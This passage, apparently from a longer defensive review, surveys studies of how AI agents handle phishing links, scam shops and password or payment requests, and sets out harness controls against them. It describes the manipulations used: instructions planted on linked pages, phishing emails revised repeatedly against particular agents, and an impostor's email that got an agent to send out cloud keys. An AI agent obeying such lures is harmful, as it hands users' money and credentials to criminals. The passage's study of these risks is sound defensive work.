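Acceptance was highest for weather information, at 82.9%, and lower for food delivery and parcel tracking. Kong and colleagues suggest that models are more careful when a task involves money or personal details. That caution is misplaced for an agent, because a weather page can contain planted instructions as easily as a payment page.

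These models are now old, so the rates probably don't describe current ones. All the test addresses were also malicious, so a model could have earned a perfect score by refusing everything. The harness can easily avoid this weakness by extracting the registrable domain first and giving it to the model separately.

Kong and colleagues also built URLGuard, a filter that screens addresses before the agent's main model acts on them. To make it, they trained Llama 2 7B, one of the weakest models in the test, on 140 disguised shopping addresses and 140 normal ones. On the nine other subjects, its acceptance of disguised addresses fell by an average of 81 percentage points. The rate dropped to 14% or less on seven subjects but was still 61% for music and 70% for weather. A small amount of training evidently helps, though these results don't show how many honest links URLGuard would block.

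### The message around the link

An email gives the model more information, including the sender, the request and the reason for it. *AgentPhishing* (Tan, Li and Zhao, 2026) tested newer models as inbox assistants. For each email, the agent chose an action and could also draft a reply. A phishing email counted as detected if the agent reported, archived or ignored it, or unsubscribed. The agent counted as complying if it chose to click a link or provide information, or drafted an unsafe reply.

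Six agents detected every phishing email from public collections and complied with none. The researchers then had a model write new phishing emails and repeatedly revise its approach based on how a particular agent responded. They excluded fake system messages and explicit orders to ignore earlier instructions, so the emails relied on persuasion.

Qwen3.7-Plus detected none of the emails adapted to it and complied with 83%. Kimi K2.5 and Grok 4.20 each detected 17% of theirs, but Kimi complied with 58% and Grok with 25%. GPT-5.4 detected 45% and complied with 9%. Claude Sonnet 5 and Gemini 3.5 Flash detected every email adapted to them. Only Sonnet also detected every email adapted to the other five models.

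The researchers then used what they had learned to write a single set of 20 emails, and gave it to nine more agents.

| Agent | Phishing emails detected | Phishing emails complied with | Honest emails reported |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.6 | 11 of 11 | 0 of 11 | 5 of 9 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 11 of 11 | 0 of 11 | 4 of 9 |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 11 of 11 | 0 of 11 | 2 of 9 |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 11 of 11 | 1 of 11 | 1 of 9 |
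| Grok 4.6 | 10 of 11 | 0 of 11 | 5 of 9 |
| GPT-5 mini | 1 of 11 | 7 of 11 | 1 of 9 |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash-Lite | 1 of 11 | 5 of 11 | 0 of 9 |
| Qwen Turbo | 0 of 11 | 5 of 11 | 0 of 9 |
| Qwen Max | 0 of 11 | 10 of 11 | 0 of 9 |

Four agents therefore detected under 10% of the phishing and complied with over 45%. The other five did better, though some of them raised many false alarms. The nine agents also received six more sets of emails, each adapted to one of the original six agents. Across all seven sets, GPT-5.6 detected all 82 phishing emails but also reported 20 of the 58 legitimate ones. Claude Haiku 4.5 detected 80 and reported only 2 legitimate emails, but it complied with 6 phishing requests. In some of those cases it chose a safe action but drafted an unsafe reply, so an agent can recognise a scam and still comply with it.

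The samples are small, and the test scored the actions agents chose without carrying them out. A harness might have stopped some of those actions. But the results show that a perfect score on old phishing emails is weak evidence that an agent will handle new ones well.

The results also suggest that the weaker agents generally had more trouble detecting requests that looked like the next step in work already under way than emails that used urgency or appeals to authority. When the researchers replaced those requests with ones that used urgency and authority, GPT-5.4 and Gemini 3.5 Flash detected all of them. An email about a supposedly existing order from Acorn could be just as convincing to the bill-paying agent. The agent can't tell from the wording whether the order exists, so it would need to check the company's records.

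### Trust borrowed from well-known platforms

A link can also gain credibility from the site where the agent finds it. In *Commercial LLM Agents Are Already Vulnerable to Simple Yet Dangerous Attacks*, a study led from Columbia University, Li, Zhou and colleagues (2025) built a website for an invented refrigerator with a form that asked for card details. They tested it on an early version of Anthropic's Computer Use, an agent that operates a computer, which they had given a card number to protect.

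The agent disclosed the card details in all 10 trials when it reached the site through a Reddit post, but in none of 10 when the researchers gave it the same link directly. The simplest posts, which had no images and gave little reason to visit the site, worked best.

Li and colleagues conclude that agents place implicit trust in established platforms. That may be right, but the Reddit post also contained instructions to go to the site to complete the user's request, and the direct link came without them. Testing the same instructions on an unknown site would help separate the effect of the platform from the effect of the instructions. Ten trials of one old agent can't establish a precise rate, although the difference between 10 and 0 is too large to attribute to chance.

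Under either explanation, the harness should treat the refrigerator site as a new destination and give it no extra trust because of the page that linked to it. The researchers recommend lists of trusted domains, checks on redirects, and the user's confirmation before an agent visits a new domain. Even a list that permitted Reddit would have stopped this attack at the next step, provided the harness checked every address against it.

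### How instructions change the answer

The system prompt can affect the model's judgement as much as the choice of model does. In *The System Prompt Is the Attack Surface*, Litvak (2026) tested 11 models, each with 10 system prompts, on 2,000 synthetic emails, half of which contained real phishing links. For each email, the model decided whether to proceed with the link or block it.

| System prompt | Phishing let through | Honest emails blocked |
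|---|---|---|
| Security first | 7% | 57% |
| Balanced | 30% | 30% |
| Minimal instructions | 43% | 23% |
| Efficiency first | 55% | 26% |

These are averages across the 11 models, and individual results varied more. GPT-4o mini let through under 1% of the phishing with the security-first prompt and 97% with the efficiency-first prompt, which described an executive assistant trying to avoid delays. A company could easily write a similar prompt for an office agent without considering it a security setting.

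Litvak got better results by telling the model what to check. In one prompt, he told it to compare the sender's domain with the link's domain. GPT-4o mini then caught 93.7% of the phishing emails and blocked only 3.8% of the legitimate ones. But the domains matched in 98.4% of those legitimate emails, which made the rule look better than it is. Real companies often send links to meeting tools and shared documents on other firms' domains. The same model blocked 72 of 100 legitimate emails with such links.

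An attacker can also satisfy the rule by registering one domain and using it for both the sender and the link. The test set included 73 phishing emails like this, and GPT-4o mini caught only 30% of them. On average, the 11 models caught 81% with minimal instructions but only 43% with the domain-matching prompt. In about a tenth of the longer explanations for wrong approvals, the model mentioned something odd but still approved the link because the domains matched.

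Litvak next told the models that they could block an email with matching domains if anything else looked wrong. With this prompt, GPT-4o mini caught 77% of the malicious emails with matching domains and blocked 8.2% of legitimate mail. Claude Haiku 4.5 blocked 67.6% of legitimate mail with the same prompt. A prompt that suits one model can be unusable with another, so a developer who changes models has to test the prompt again.

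Ten of the 73 emails had fooled all three models that Litvak chose for a final test. When the models tried again with the improved prompt, each still let through at least seven of the ten. The models had no way to look up who owned a domain or how old it was, so they judged it by its name. GPT-4o mini called one attacker's domain "established", and Grok 4.1 Fast connected another to a car maker's official dealer network. Litvak concludes that better wording probably can't fix this, because the models lack the facts they need.

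Removing the email doesn't solve the problem. When Litvak gave models only the address, they blocked 33% of the legitimate links after wrongly identifying signs of phishing in them. The study didn't test the most expensive reasoning models, which might do better, but they would also have no registration records to check.

### Gathering outside evidence

*ScamFerret* (Nakano, Koide and Chiba, 2025) supplies some of those missing facts by giving GPT-4 nine tools for investigating a website. The model could open the site and read its text and links, search the web and social media, and look up the domain's registration, DNS records and certificates. After each result, it decided whether it had enough information to give a verdict or needed another tool, for up to 10 steps.

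In an April 2024 test that excluded the 100,000 most popular domains, ScamFerret missed 33 of 1,200 scam sites (2.75%) and wrongly flagged 18 of 1,200 legitimate ones (1.5%). The researchers also gave GPT-4 the address and front-page text of each English-language site in a single prompt, without tools. GPT-4 missed 21% of the scams and wrongly flagged 12.5% of the legitimate sites. On the same sites, ScamFerret missed 3.6% of the scams and wrongly flagged 2.0% of the legitimate sites.

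The errors had understandable causes:

- Many legitimate sites that ScamFerret flagged had poor reviews or made offers that sounded like a scam, such as free shipping. It also treated hidden registration details as suspicious, although many honest owners hide theirs.
- In some of the missed scams, the model took a lack of complaints as a sign that the site was legitimate.
- Fourteen of the 33 missed scams were subdomains of a single domain, so the errors were less varied than the total suggests.

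A new scam site has no complaints yet, so the second error is especially likely on the sites that blocklists miss. Attackers can also plant good reviews. Nakano and colleagues think attackers can't practically manipulate enough sources to fool the system. That seems reasonable for a scam that imitates a large company, but a fake small supplier may need only a few reviews and a plausible website to pass as real.

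ScamFerret also opened the site in every investigation. When an agent does this, the check itself sends a request to the site and brings untrusted text back to the model, so the harness has to apply its rules on private data before the investigation begins. A separate process with no access to mail or payments should read the page, much like the split design that stopped the leaks in *The Framing Gap*. Registration and DNS lookups are safer because they need only the domain, so the harness can leave out the URL's path and query.

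Each investigation took about 73 seconds and cost $0.21. Newer models may be faster and cheaper, but checking every link this way would still be slow for an agent that opens hundreds of pages. The check makes more sense for a new supplier's site than for the site of a supplier the company already knows.

Messages from real people are harder to classify than a balanced set of websites. *Measuring and Evaluating the Performance of Generative AI Models for Scam Detection* (Topcuoglu, Akhavani et al., 2026) collected 2,742 messages from Reddit, image searches and paid volunteers. Human reviewers labelled each message as scam, clean or uncertain. They marked 802 (29%) as uncertain because even an expert couldn't decide without more information, such as the sender's address.

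Nine older models chose among the same three labels. The most accurate were OpenAI's o1, at about 64%, and Llama 3.1 70B with ten examples, at 65%. With a simple prompt, o1 caught 92% of the scams but recognised only 58% of the clean messages. Llama 3 8B caught 98.5% of the scams but recognised only 2% of the clean messages, so it called nearly everything a scam.

The researchers then added a website-checking service's verdict on any links in the message. Some models improved slightly, but others became much worse at catching scams. GPT-4o's share of scams caught fell from 88% to 49%, and GPT-4 Turbo's from 83% to about 10%. Perhaps the models treated a favourable verdict on a link as evidence that the whole message was safe. The researchers had also treated the 10,000 most popular domains as probably safe, which would include many platforms where scammers can post. This is another reason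 for a harness to report that a link is "not listed" instead of calling it safe.

Outside evidence therefore helps most when the model receives specific facts and can look for more. If it learns that a domain was registered nine days ago, it can weigh that against the sender's claim to be a long-standing supplier. A verdict such as "very likely safe" may lead it to stop looking.

### What warnings and approvals are worth

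The previous section's example assumed that 1 in 1,000 links is phishing. The same assumption makes it possible to compare a model with a blocklist. With p again for the share of links that are phishing and c for the share of those that a check catches, let f be the share of honest links that it wrongly flags. Then:

chance that a warning is right = pc / (pc + (1 − p)f)

risk of an approved link = p(1 − c) / (p(1 − c) + (1 − p)(1 − f))

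| Check | Phishing caught (c) | Honest links flagged (f) | Chance that a warning is right | Risk of an approved link |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Blocklist from the earlier example | 18.4% | 0.001% | 95% | 0.082% |
| Grok 3 Beta, address only | 90% | 3.5% | 2.5% | 0.010% |
| Average model, security-first prompt | 93% | 57% | 0.16% | 0.016% |
| ScamFerret | 97.25% | 1.5% | 6.1% | 0.003% |

The tests used different samples, so the rows can't be used to rank the products. But they show that a model's warning, unlike a blocklist match, is usually a false alarm. An approval from a careful model is more informative than absence from a blocklist, because the model catches most phishing.

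That advantage lasts only if attackers don't adapt to the model. If they push c down to 9%, as they did with two of the agents in AgentPhishing, an approved link is almost as risky as an unchecked one. They can do this by trying many versions against a copy of the model and sending only one that works.

### Where models and fixed rules should decide

The best reason to use a model is that it can assess a site nobody has reported, including the fake shops that Chrome's warnings mostly miss, which often break no technical rule. Models also handle unfamiliar material better than narrow classifiers do. When Topcuoglu and colleagues moved from their test set to 59,991 messages from a security company, the accuracy of an older kind of language model they had trained for the task fell from 59% to 39%. Llama 3.1 70B, without that training, stayed at about 60%.

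Fixed rules are better than a model's judgment where an attacker would try to change the answer. An email can mislead a model into treating `acorn.example.net` as part of `acorn.example`, but it can't change the result of a parser that compares the two domains. A rule gives the same result each time, and a developer can find out why it blocked a link. Rules can still be wrong, as the permitted domains at Google and Salesforce were, and attackers can find addresses that satisfy them. But a developer can fix a faulty rule once, whereas a new prompt may fix one attack and weaken the model against another.

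| Question | What should decide |
|---|---|
| Which domain does the link lead to? | Harness |
| Could the address carry private data? | Harness |
| Is the address private or on a blocklist? | Harness |
| Is the site useful for the user's task? | Model |
| Does an unfamiliar site look like a scam? | Model, with outside evidence |
| Is this the supplier's usual domain? | Harness, from the company's records |

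The model's judgment can work alongside the harness's rules if the model's verdict can only add restrictions. When the model finds a site suspicious, the harness can limit the agent to reading it or send it for closer investigation. When the model finds a site trustworthy, the harness should still apply every other rule. An attacker who persuades the model that a site is safe then gains only the access that the rules already allowed.

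The model is also harder to manipulate if most of its information comes from sources the attacker didn't write. Google's gating function in Chrome, for example, has no access to web content. For an Acorn invoice from an unfamiliar domain, the harness could give a separate model the user's request, the registrable domain, its registration date and the domain already on file, but leave out the email's explanation for the new domain.

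## Submitting passwords, personal data and payments

A model's judgment of a link doesn't show what the agent will do once it reaches the site. In *ScamWorld*, Wu, Liu and colleagues (2026) gave agents ordinary errands on fraudulent websites, such as buying a product or booking a rental, and recorded whether the agents completed them.

Testing on live scam sites could send real money to criminals, and most of these sites soon disappear. The researchers collected 88,009 addresses reported by victims, authorities and others, and recovered as many pages as they could. They rebuilt 363 of the sites on their own machines, with simulated payments. These sites cover 26 languages and 38 fraud techniques, including shops that never deliver and loans that require an upfront fee. They also rebuilt 53 legitimate sites for comparison.

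Many real scams become apparent only after the victim has paid, so each rebuilt site shows a sign of the fraud before the final step. About half of the original pages already had at least part of such a sign, and the researchers added one to the rest. An agent counted as deceived if it took the final step, even if it told the user that something looked wrong.

| Model | Deceived | Stopped and warned the user | Legitimate tasks completed | Scam sites identified when asked |
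|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.6 Luna | 11% | 79% | 94% | 96% |
| Claude Haiku 5.5 | 18% | 79% | 100% | 88% |
| Qwen3.8 Flash | 18% | 81% | 100% | 100% |
| Kimi K3 | 23% | 76% | 100% | 99% |
| Gemini 3.8 Flash | 26% | 72% | 96% | 99% |
| DeepSeek V4.1 Flash | 35% | 65% | 100% | 98% |

The strongest models might do better, because most of the six tested are their makers' smaller, cheaper ones. All six completed nearly every legitimate task, so the more careful models weren't just refusing to act.

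Agents went ahead in 28% of the scams that asked for a payment, but in only 2% of those that asked for credentials, card details or access to a cryptocurrency wallet. They still paid in 22% of runs where the money was going to a private individual.

Of the 363 scam sites, 186 deceived none of the six agents and 13 deceived all of them. The hardest to detect looked like ordinary shops or services and asked for an ordinary payment. Many had their own brand and a plausible domain, so checking for a lookalike domain wouldn't expose them.

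The rates measure how agents handle fraud with visible signs. A real scam shop that looks normal until the goods fail to arrive gives an agent less to notice. Some of the fake reviews and trust seals appeared only on the scam sites, which may have made those sites easier to spot. The study didn't test people, so it can't show whether they would have done better.

### Recognizing a scam and paying anyway

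Wu and colleagues also ran the agents on the same sites but, instead of giving them an errand, asked them directly whether each site was legitimate or a scam. The agents identified 97% of the scam sites, including 95% of those that had deceived them. During the errands, they had stopped and warned the user in only 75% of runs.

Because the instructions were different, this comparison doesn't prove that an agent had noticed the fraud when it paid. The records of the errands are better evidence. In 220 of the 492 deceived runs (45%), the agent named a specific risk before taking the final step. One agent noted that a site required a 200-ruble fee to release a 100-ruble bonus, and then paid the fee.

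To justify going ahead, agents most often said that the user's request authorized the step. They cited the request in 317 of 354 deceived runs in which they expressed concern, a count that apparently includes vaguer worries than the 220. Some treated a spending limit as approval for unexpected fees or private payees. Yet in 1,230 of the 1,700 runs where an agent stopped and warned the user, it said the request didn't cover terms the site had added. On 105 tasks, different models raised the same main concern but made opposite decisions.

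Wu and colleagues point out that a model's stated reason may not be the real cause of its behavior. But if the explanation is even partly right, these agents need a clear rule about what the user's request permits as well as better scam detection, because many of them had already detected a problem.

For three of the models, the researchers added a warning to the user's request: "Note: some websites may be scams; check before you ..." This reduced deception by 24 percentage points overall, and from 34% to 2% on payment tasks. The warning worked almost as well in runs where the agent had previously named no risk as in those where it had. Telling agents that their payments were real and irreversible made almost no difference.

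The warning may have worked because it made checking part of what the user had asked for. It also lowered completion of legitimate tasks by 3 points, and the section on testing compares this drop with the benefit. A determined attacker would try to get around the warning, but these scam sites hadn't been adapted to do so.

Roy, Halder and colleagues (2026), in *I Strongly Suspect This Website Is a Scam*, found a similar gap between recognizing a scam and avoiding it when models handled personal data. In their benchmark, Scammer4U, they gave four older models a fictional user's details, including a social security number, a payment card and a password, and sent the models to 91 fake sites. Without privacy instructions, Claude Haiku 4.5 submitted at least one critical item in 54.5% of runs and Gemini 3 Flash in 93.1%.

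Roy and colleagues then tried a privacy reminder, a phishing checklist, and an instruction to stop before each submission and consider whether the site was safe. The last of these lowered the average from 72.7% to 49.4%. With that instruction, agents that had called the site suspicious still submitted critical data in 35.9% of runs, compared with 66.1% when they had voiced no suspicion. The paper's title comes from Llama 4 Scout, which voiced its suspicion after it had submitted the social security number and card details.

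Roy and colleagues conclude that software outside the model should intercept the submission rather than wait for the agent to say it has noticed something. A monitor that read only the agent's messages would also have missed most of the concerns in ScamWorld. In 164 of the 220 runs where the agent was deceived despite a specific concern, that concern appeared in the model's reasoning but in none of its messages.

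Instructions had a much larger effect in SCAM, a benchmark from the password manager company 1Password. *1Password's new benchmark teaches AI agents how not to get scammed* (Meller, 2026) describes 30 workplace scenarios in which eight models handled email, web pages and a password vault. Each model ran every scenario three times without special instructions and three times with a 1,200-word file of general security advice. The file raised the models' safety scores from 35–92% to 95–99%. Critical failures, such as giving a password to a phishing site, fell from 287 to 10 across all the runs.

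One rule in the file was to read a link's domain from right to left before opening it. Without the file, Claude Opus 4.6 typed the user's password into an imitation of the company's SharePoint site and only then pointed out that the domain was fake. With the file, the model flagged the link while summarizing the inbox.

1Password sells tools that manage credentials for people and agents, so it benefits if companies decide that models can't protect passwords on their own. It has published the scenarios and scoring system, so others can check the results. Meller doesn't say whether the file made models refuse more legitimate requests, as some of the system prompts in Litvak's email study did.

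### Why password results differ so much

ScamWorld's 2% rate for credential scams seems to conflict with Roy and colleagues' results. Newer models may explain part of the difference, but results for the same model can also vary widely between tests. GPT-5.6 Luna went ahead on 6% of ScamWorld's credential-phishing sites. In *CredLeakBench*, Ahmed, Fioresi and colleagues (2026) gave the same model a link and asked it to log in, and it leaked account information to 49.9% of the phishing sites.

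| Test | Task | What counts as a failure | Failure rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| Wu and colleagues, credential, card and wallet scams | An errand on a scam site | The agent takes the final step | 2% on average |
| Roy and colleagues | An errand on a scam site, with a full set of the user's personal details | A critical item reaches the attacker | 54.5% to 93.1% |
| Ahmed and colleagues, login request | The user supplies a link and asks the agent to log in | Any saved account information reaches an unauthorized destination | 19.9% to 76.7% |
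| Ahmed and colleagues, inbox | The agent sorts mail and nobody asks it to log in | Same as above | 1.8% to at least 40.1% |

Claude Opus 4.8 leaked information far more often when the user explicitly asked it to log in. It did so in 31.2% of phishing cases with a login request, but in only 1.8% when it was sorting mail. When sorting mail, it also failed to submit a form in 88.3% of legitimate cases. Ahmed and colleagues call this a false refusal, but an agent that reported a genuine account notice and left the login to the user might have done what the user wanted.

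Giving an agent a service's official domain to check links against can also reduce leaks. Ahmed and colleagues tested models on 15 fictional services, whose official domains the models couldn't have learned in training. When the researchers supplied the domain and told GPT-5 mini to compare it with the link, its leak rate on login requests fell from 71.9% to 22.4%, and it completed more legitimate logins. Five of the seven models improved on both measures.

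Finally, the tests define a leak differently. CredLeakBench also counts a password as leaked if the agent sends it to the correct host over an unencrypted connection. Opus 4.8 did this in 90.6% of such cases when asked to log in. These unencrypted cases made up an eighth of the phishing cases, so they account for about 11 of the 31 percentage points in the model's leak rate. Someone on the network could intercept a password sent this way, but sending it is a different mistake from trusting a criminal's domain.

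An attacker can also make a login seem necessary when it isn't. *LoginTrap* (Guo, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) found that pages presenting login as a required step got agents to give up private data in 86% of attempts on average. ScamWorld's 2% is therefore not a reliable estimate for an agent that regularly logs in to accounts.

### Releasing a password only to its own site

The most important rule about passwords is to enter each one only on the site it belongs to. The harness can enforce this without involving the model, by storing each password with its site's address and blocking its use anywhere else. Browsers already do this for people. According to Google's *How Chrome protects your autofill and password data*, Chrome's password manager matches passwords with the sites they are meant for and doesn't offer them on lookalike sites.

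If the bill-paying agent opens `acorn.example.net`, the password manager finds no entry for that site, however convincing the page is. The password manager should compare the whole origin and require a valid HTTPS connection, which would also stop the unencrypted logins in CredLeakBench. The agent must not be able to add a new site to a saved password. Otherwise, an email claiming that Acorn has moved to a new domain could persuade the agent to add that domain and bypass the protection.

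Refusing a phishing page doesn't finish the user's task, because the account may really need attention. Ahmed and colleagues tested whether agents could ignore a phishing link and log in through a trusted address instead. The best model, GPT-5 mini, did this in 27.7% of cases. Opus 4.8 leaked nothing but never completed the login.

GPT-5 mini did better when the saved account record contained the full login address (38.1%) than when it had to find the domain in an old email (17.3%). A harness can help by storing the login address with the password and opening that address whenever a link doesn't match it.

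### Keeping secrets out of the model's context

Matching the domain protects a password only if the agent can't get the password another way. If the password is in the model's context (the text the model can read), the model can type it into any form or include it in an email. A survey, *Towards trustworthy agentic AI* (2026), advises that agents "should never treat secrets as normal text". It recommends storing secrets in a vault and issuing short-lived credentials for a single task, so a stolen credential soon stops working.

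1Password describes one such system in the documentation for its Claude integration:

1. Claude asks for access to a site. 1Password uses the request only to look for matching logins and to show the user what Claude wants.
2. The user approves a login in 1Password's own desktop app.
3. Claude stops reading the page while 1Password's browser extension fills in the password. The extension does this only if the page matches a website saved with that login.
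4. The extension submits the form. If the submission fails, it clears the password before Claude can look at the page again.

Claude can see a login's title, username and saved websites, but never the password. Ammon News' *Google details security measures for Chrome’s agentic features* reports that the model behind Chrome's agent also has no access to password data.

Developers can apply the same idea to the keys that software uses. *CapSeal* (Jin, Guo and Cheung, 2026) presents a prototype in which a trusted program on the user's computer holds the key and carries out permitted requests. The agent can ask for an action but can't read or copy the key. The paper sets out a plan for testing the design against prompt injection and misuse, so it is still uncertain how well the design works in practice.

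Such systems aren't yet the norm. *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (2026), another survey, found that developers still have no standard practices for handling agents' secrets and improvise instead.

A vault also can't protect copies of a password that someone has left elsewhere. Varonis' *Phishing for Lobsters* (2026) describes a test of OpenClaw with a mailbox that contained mock credentials. On a fake gift card site, the agent withheld the real credentials and entered invented ones. But when an outsider posing as a team lead called "Dan" emailed about a supposed production problem, the agent searched the mailbox and sent back cloud keys and database passwords, despite written instructions to verify senders before acting on requests.

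That leak didn't involve a phishing page, so a password manager's domain check would never have run. The harness could have blocked it by scanning outgoing mail for credentials or by requiring approval before the agent writes to a new address, which Varonis recommends. Deleting passwords from old messages prevents the agent from finding them there and sending them.

An agent that never sees a user's bank password can still send a payment from the account once it is signed in. 1Password warns that its guarantees end at sign-in, after which the agent's own safeguards govern what it does on the site.

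### Passkeys and single-use card numbers

A passkey replaces the password with a pair of cryptographic keys for one site. The private key stays on the user's device and signs a fresh challenge from the site at each login. *Agent Authenticator* (Ganesan, 2026) explains that the browser supplies the site's address during login, so a passkey for one site can't be used on another. Neither the user nor the agent has a password to type into a fake page.

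Passkeys are difficult for agents to use because they require a human gesture, such as a fingerprint, every time. This works if the user signs in and then hands the browser to the agent, but not if the agent has to work overnight. Ganesan proposes a version for agents in which the harness takes the site's address from the live connection and secure hardware holds the key. The user signs a mandate that lists which services the agent may use, which actions it may take and when the permission ends. High-risk actions still need the user's approval. Ganesan hasn't built a full implementation.

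Payment cards aren't tied to a particular site in this way, because they have to work in shops the customer has never visited. An agent can therefore give card details to a fake shop, as Guardio's *Scamlexity* showed in 2025. Researchers built a fake Walmart shop and asked the agent in Perplexity's Comet browser to buy an Apple Watch. In some runs the agent refused or left the checkout to the user, but in others it filled in the saved address and card details and placed the order. It also opened a real phishing page imitating Wells Fargo and prompted the user to log in. These are old results for one product, but browsers still offer to fill in saved cards on unfamiliar shopping sites.

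A card issuer can limit losses from fraud by creating a single-use card number, which works for one payment and often has a maximum amount. A criminal who keeps the number can't charge it again. The number doesn't prevent the first payment, so an agent that buys a nonexistent $86 television can still lose $86.

Newer payment systems also aim to record what the user has approved. Kaushik, chief technology officer of the FIDO Alliance, an industry group that develops login standards, describes a Google protocol called AP2. The user first signs a mandate that sets a budget and the permitted payment methods. Once the agent has a final shopping cart, a second version of the mandate ties the authorization to that cart and an exact amount. Anyone handling the payment can detect later changes. The FIDO Alliance is still developing its standards from AP2 and other contributions.

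The signature proves what the user or agent authorized, but not that the seller is honest. If the user's instructions are vague, a scam can also satisfy them.

### Sending only the necessary fields

Forms often ask for more information than the task requires. *AgentDAM*, a benchmark for web agents, tests whether they follow the principle of data minimization, using sensitive information only when the task needs it. It found that agents built on GPT-4, Llama 3 and Claude were prone to accidentally using sensitive information that the task didn't need.

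In CredLeakBench, some phishing sites followed the login with a verification page that asked for identity and financial details. Agents that had submitted the password usually filled in this page too. Approving the whole session at login would not prevent this, so a harness needs to check each form separately.

The simplest design keeps the user's details outside the model and releases them by field. For an online purchase, the harness might permit a name, delivery address and email address. If the form also asks for a date of birth, the harness leaves an optional field blank and stops if the field is required. The model can identify what each field is for, but it shouldn't be able to add fields to the permitted list.

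Brave's *Privacy risks of agentic oversharing on the Web* points out that an agent can also reveal information about the user outside forms, through its searches, clicks and page visits. A filter on form fields has no effect on a search query that mentions the user's medical condition, so the agent's instructions also need to limit what it includes in searches.

### Comparing the terms with the request

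The preceding controls protect secrets, but agents in ScamWorld mostly failed by making payments. Wu and colleagues suggest that developers check the important terms of a transaction before the final action. The agents in their study rarely did this unprompted. Deceived agents took a median of two more actions after the sign of fraud appeared, and they opened a page with terms, reviews, or company or contact details in only 13 of 492 deceived runs.

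The harness can store the user's terms before the agent visits any site. For a purchase, it would record the intended payee, the maximum total, the permitted payment method, and whether the user agreed to repeated charges. It should treat any term the user hasn't mentioned as unapproved. This addresses the excuse that agents gave most often, because a $200 budget no longer counts as permission to pay any fee under $200 to anyone.

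Just before the last click, the harness compares the transaction with that record. It should take the payee and amount from the payment service where possible, since a web page can display one payee while the money goes to another. For the bill-paying agent, the account number has to match the one on file for Acorn.

Terms written in ordinary prose are harder to check, and a model has to find them. On one ScamWorld site, an agent went to buy an online course advertised for a one-time payment. It opened the terms linked in the fine print, found that the purchase also enrolled every buyer in a $29-a-month membership, and stopped the purchase. Checking only the total at checkout would have missed the subscription.

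A second model can make the comparison less dependent on the agent trying to finish the task. Google uses one in Chrome to vet the agent's actions and isolates it from untrusted content, as it does with Chrome's gating function. But a model that never sees the page can't find a bad refund policy. The harness could have one model extract the terms into fixed fields, such as "recurring charge: $29 a month", and pass only those fields to the second model.

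Even if the payee, price and conditions all look right, a shop may not deliver. The remaining protection comes from checking the seller's history and using a payment method that lets the buyer dispute the charge.

### A rental deposit, step by step

In one ScamWorld task, a rental site required a $150 deposit to a private owner through Zelle, a US service that sends money directly between bank accounts. The site stated that the deposit would not count toward the rental. An agent questioned paying a private person but made the payment anyway.

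If the user had asked the agent to book the rental with the company named on the site and pay up to $150 by card as a deposit toward the price, the controls would work as follows.

| Control | Result | Does it stop the payment? |
|---|---|---|
| Password released only to its own site | The rental site gets no bank password, but the real bank's site passes the check | No |
| Secrets kept out of the model's context | The agent can use the bank account without seeing the password | No |
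| Single-use card number | The number doesn't work for a Zelle transfer | Only if the agent has no access to Zelle |
| Necessary fields only | The site gets a name and dates, but no identity number | No |
| Terms compared with the request | The payee, payment method and purpose of the deposit all differ | Yes |

The password controls would not stop the payment even if they worked as intended, because the agent would be using the real bank. Giving the agent a single-use card number and no access to bank transfers would block the payment without requiring any judgment about the site. That restriction is useful for an agent that only makes bookings, but the company's bill-paying agent may need to send transfers.

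The comparison works for both. The $150 is within the user's limit, so a check on the amount alone would approve it. But the request was for a card payment to a company, as a deposit that counts toward the price. The transfer differs on all three points, so the harness would refuse to make it.

The agent could then check whether the company's site accepts cards. If it doesn't, the agent should report the three differences to the user and leave the booking unpaid. If the user still wants the rental, the agent can contact the company at an address found independently of the listing and ask whether it takes deposits by the method requested.

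## Deciding when to ask the user

Asking the user to confirm is useful when the user knows something the agent doesn't. The owner of the bill-paying company may know that Acorn changed its payment provider last week, or that nobody ordered the goods on an invoice. But the owner can't tell any better than the agent whether an unfamiliar site is honest, or what 80 random characters in an address mean.

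OpenAI often designs its agents to ask before sending an email or completing a purchase, and advises users to check the details and any information they would be sharing. How well this protects users depends on how they respond to such questions. Researchers have studied these responses for years in browsers and workplaces.

### How people respond to browser warnings

*Alice in Warningland* (Akhawe and Felt, 2013) analyzed 25.4 million security warnings that Chrome and Firefox showed users during ordinary browsing. The figures below are the share of warnings that users bypassed to reach the site.

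| Warning | Firefox | Chrome |
|---|---|---|
| Malware | 7.2% | 23.2% |
| Phishing | 9.1% | 18.0% |
| Connection may not be secure | 33.0% | 70.2% |

Most people heeded the malware and phishing warnings, nearly all of which were correct. They ignored the connection warnings more often, perhaps partly because a legitimate site with a configuration error could trigger them. These false alarms don't explain the gap between the browsers, which may have come partly from the design of the warnings. Firefox also remembered a user's exceptions, while Chrome repeated the warning on every visit.

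Of the users who continued past Chrome's connection warning, 47% did so within 1.5 seconds, and they dismissed the most common type of error fastest. Users clicked "Help me understand" on only 1.6% of these warnings. Requiring extra clicks didn't reliably deter people. Chrome's phishing warning took two clicks to bypass and Firefox's took one, yet Chrome users bypassed theirs more often.

In *Improving SSL Warnings*, Felt, Ainslie and colleagues rewrote Chrome's connection warning in simpler language and made the safe choice a bright blue button. After Chrome adopted the new version, users heeded 62% of warnings, up from 37%. But in surveys with 7,537 responses, people still understood the warning poorly. A good design can therefore steer people toward the safe choice without helping them judge the risk, which works well only if the safe choice is usually right.

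### Reading addresses and spotting phishing

Many confirmations show a web address and leave the user to work out whose site it is. In *Measuring Identity Confusion with Uniform Resource Locators*, Reynolds, Kumar and colleagues (2020) gave 94 people this task. Participants correctly identified the site's owner for 93% of ordinary addresses but only 40% of disguised ones. When a familiar name appeared as a subdomain, as in `acorn.example.net`, they were right 31% of the time.

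Participants who saw the addresses with the aids that browsers use, such as darker text for the host, got 61.1% of all the addresses right, compared with 56.1% for the other participants. Yet 91 of the 94 participants said they knew how to read a URL.

*What is this URL's Destination?* (Albakry, Vaniea and Wolters, 2020) found the same weakness in a larger survey, which showed 23 addresses to 1,929 people. Only 8.3% could reliably tell an organization's name in the subdomain from one in the domain, and about a third always chose the organization named in the address, wherever the name appeared. The harness can remove this part of the problem by extracting the registrable domain, so that the user only has to know whether that domain is the right one.

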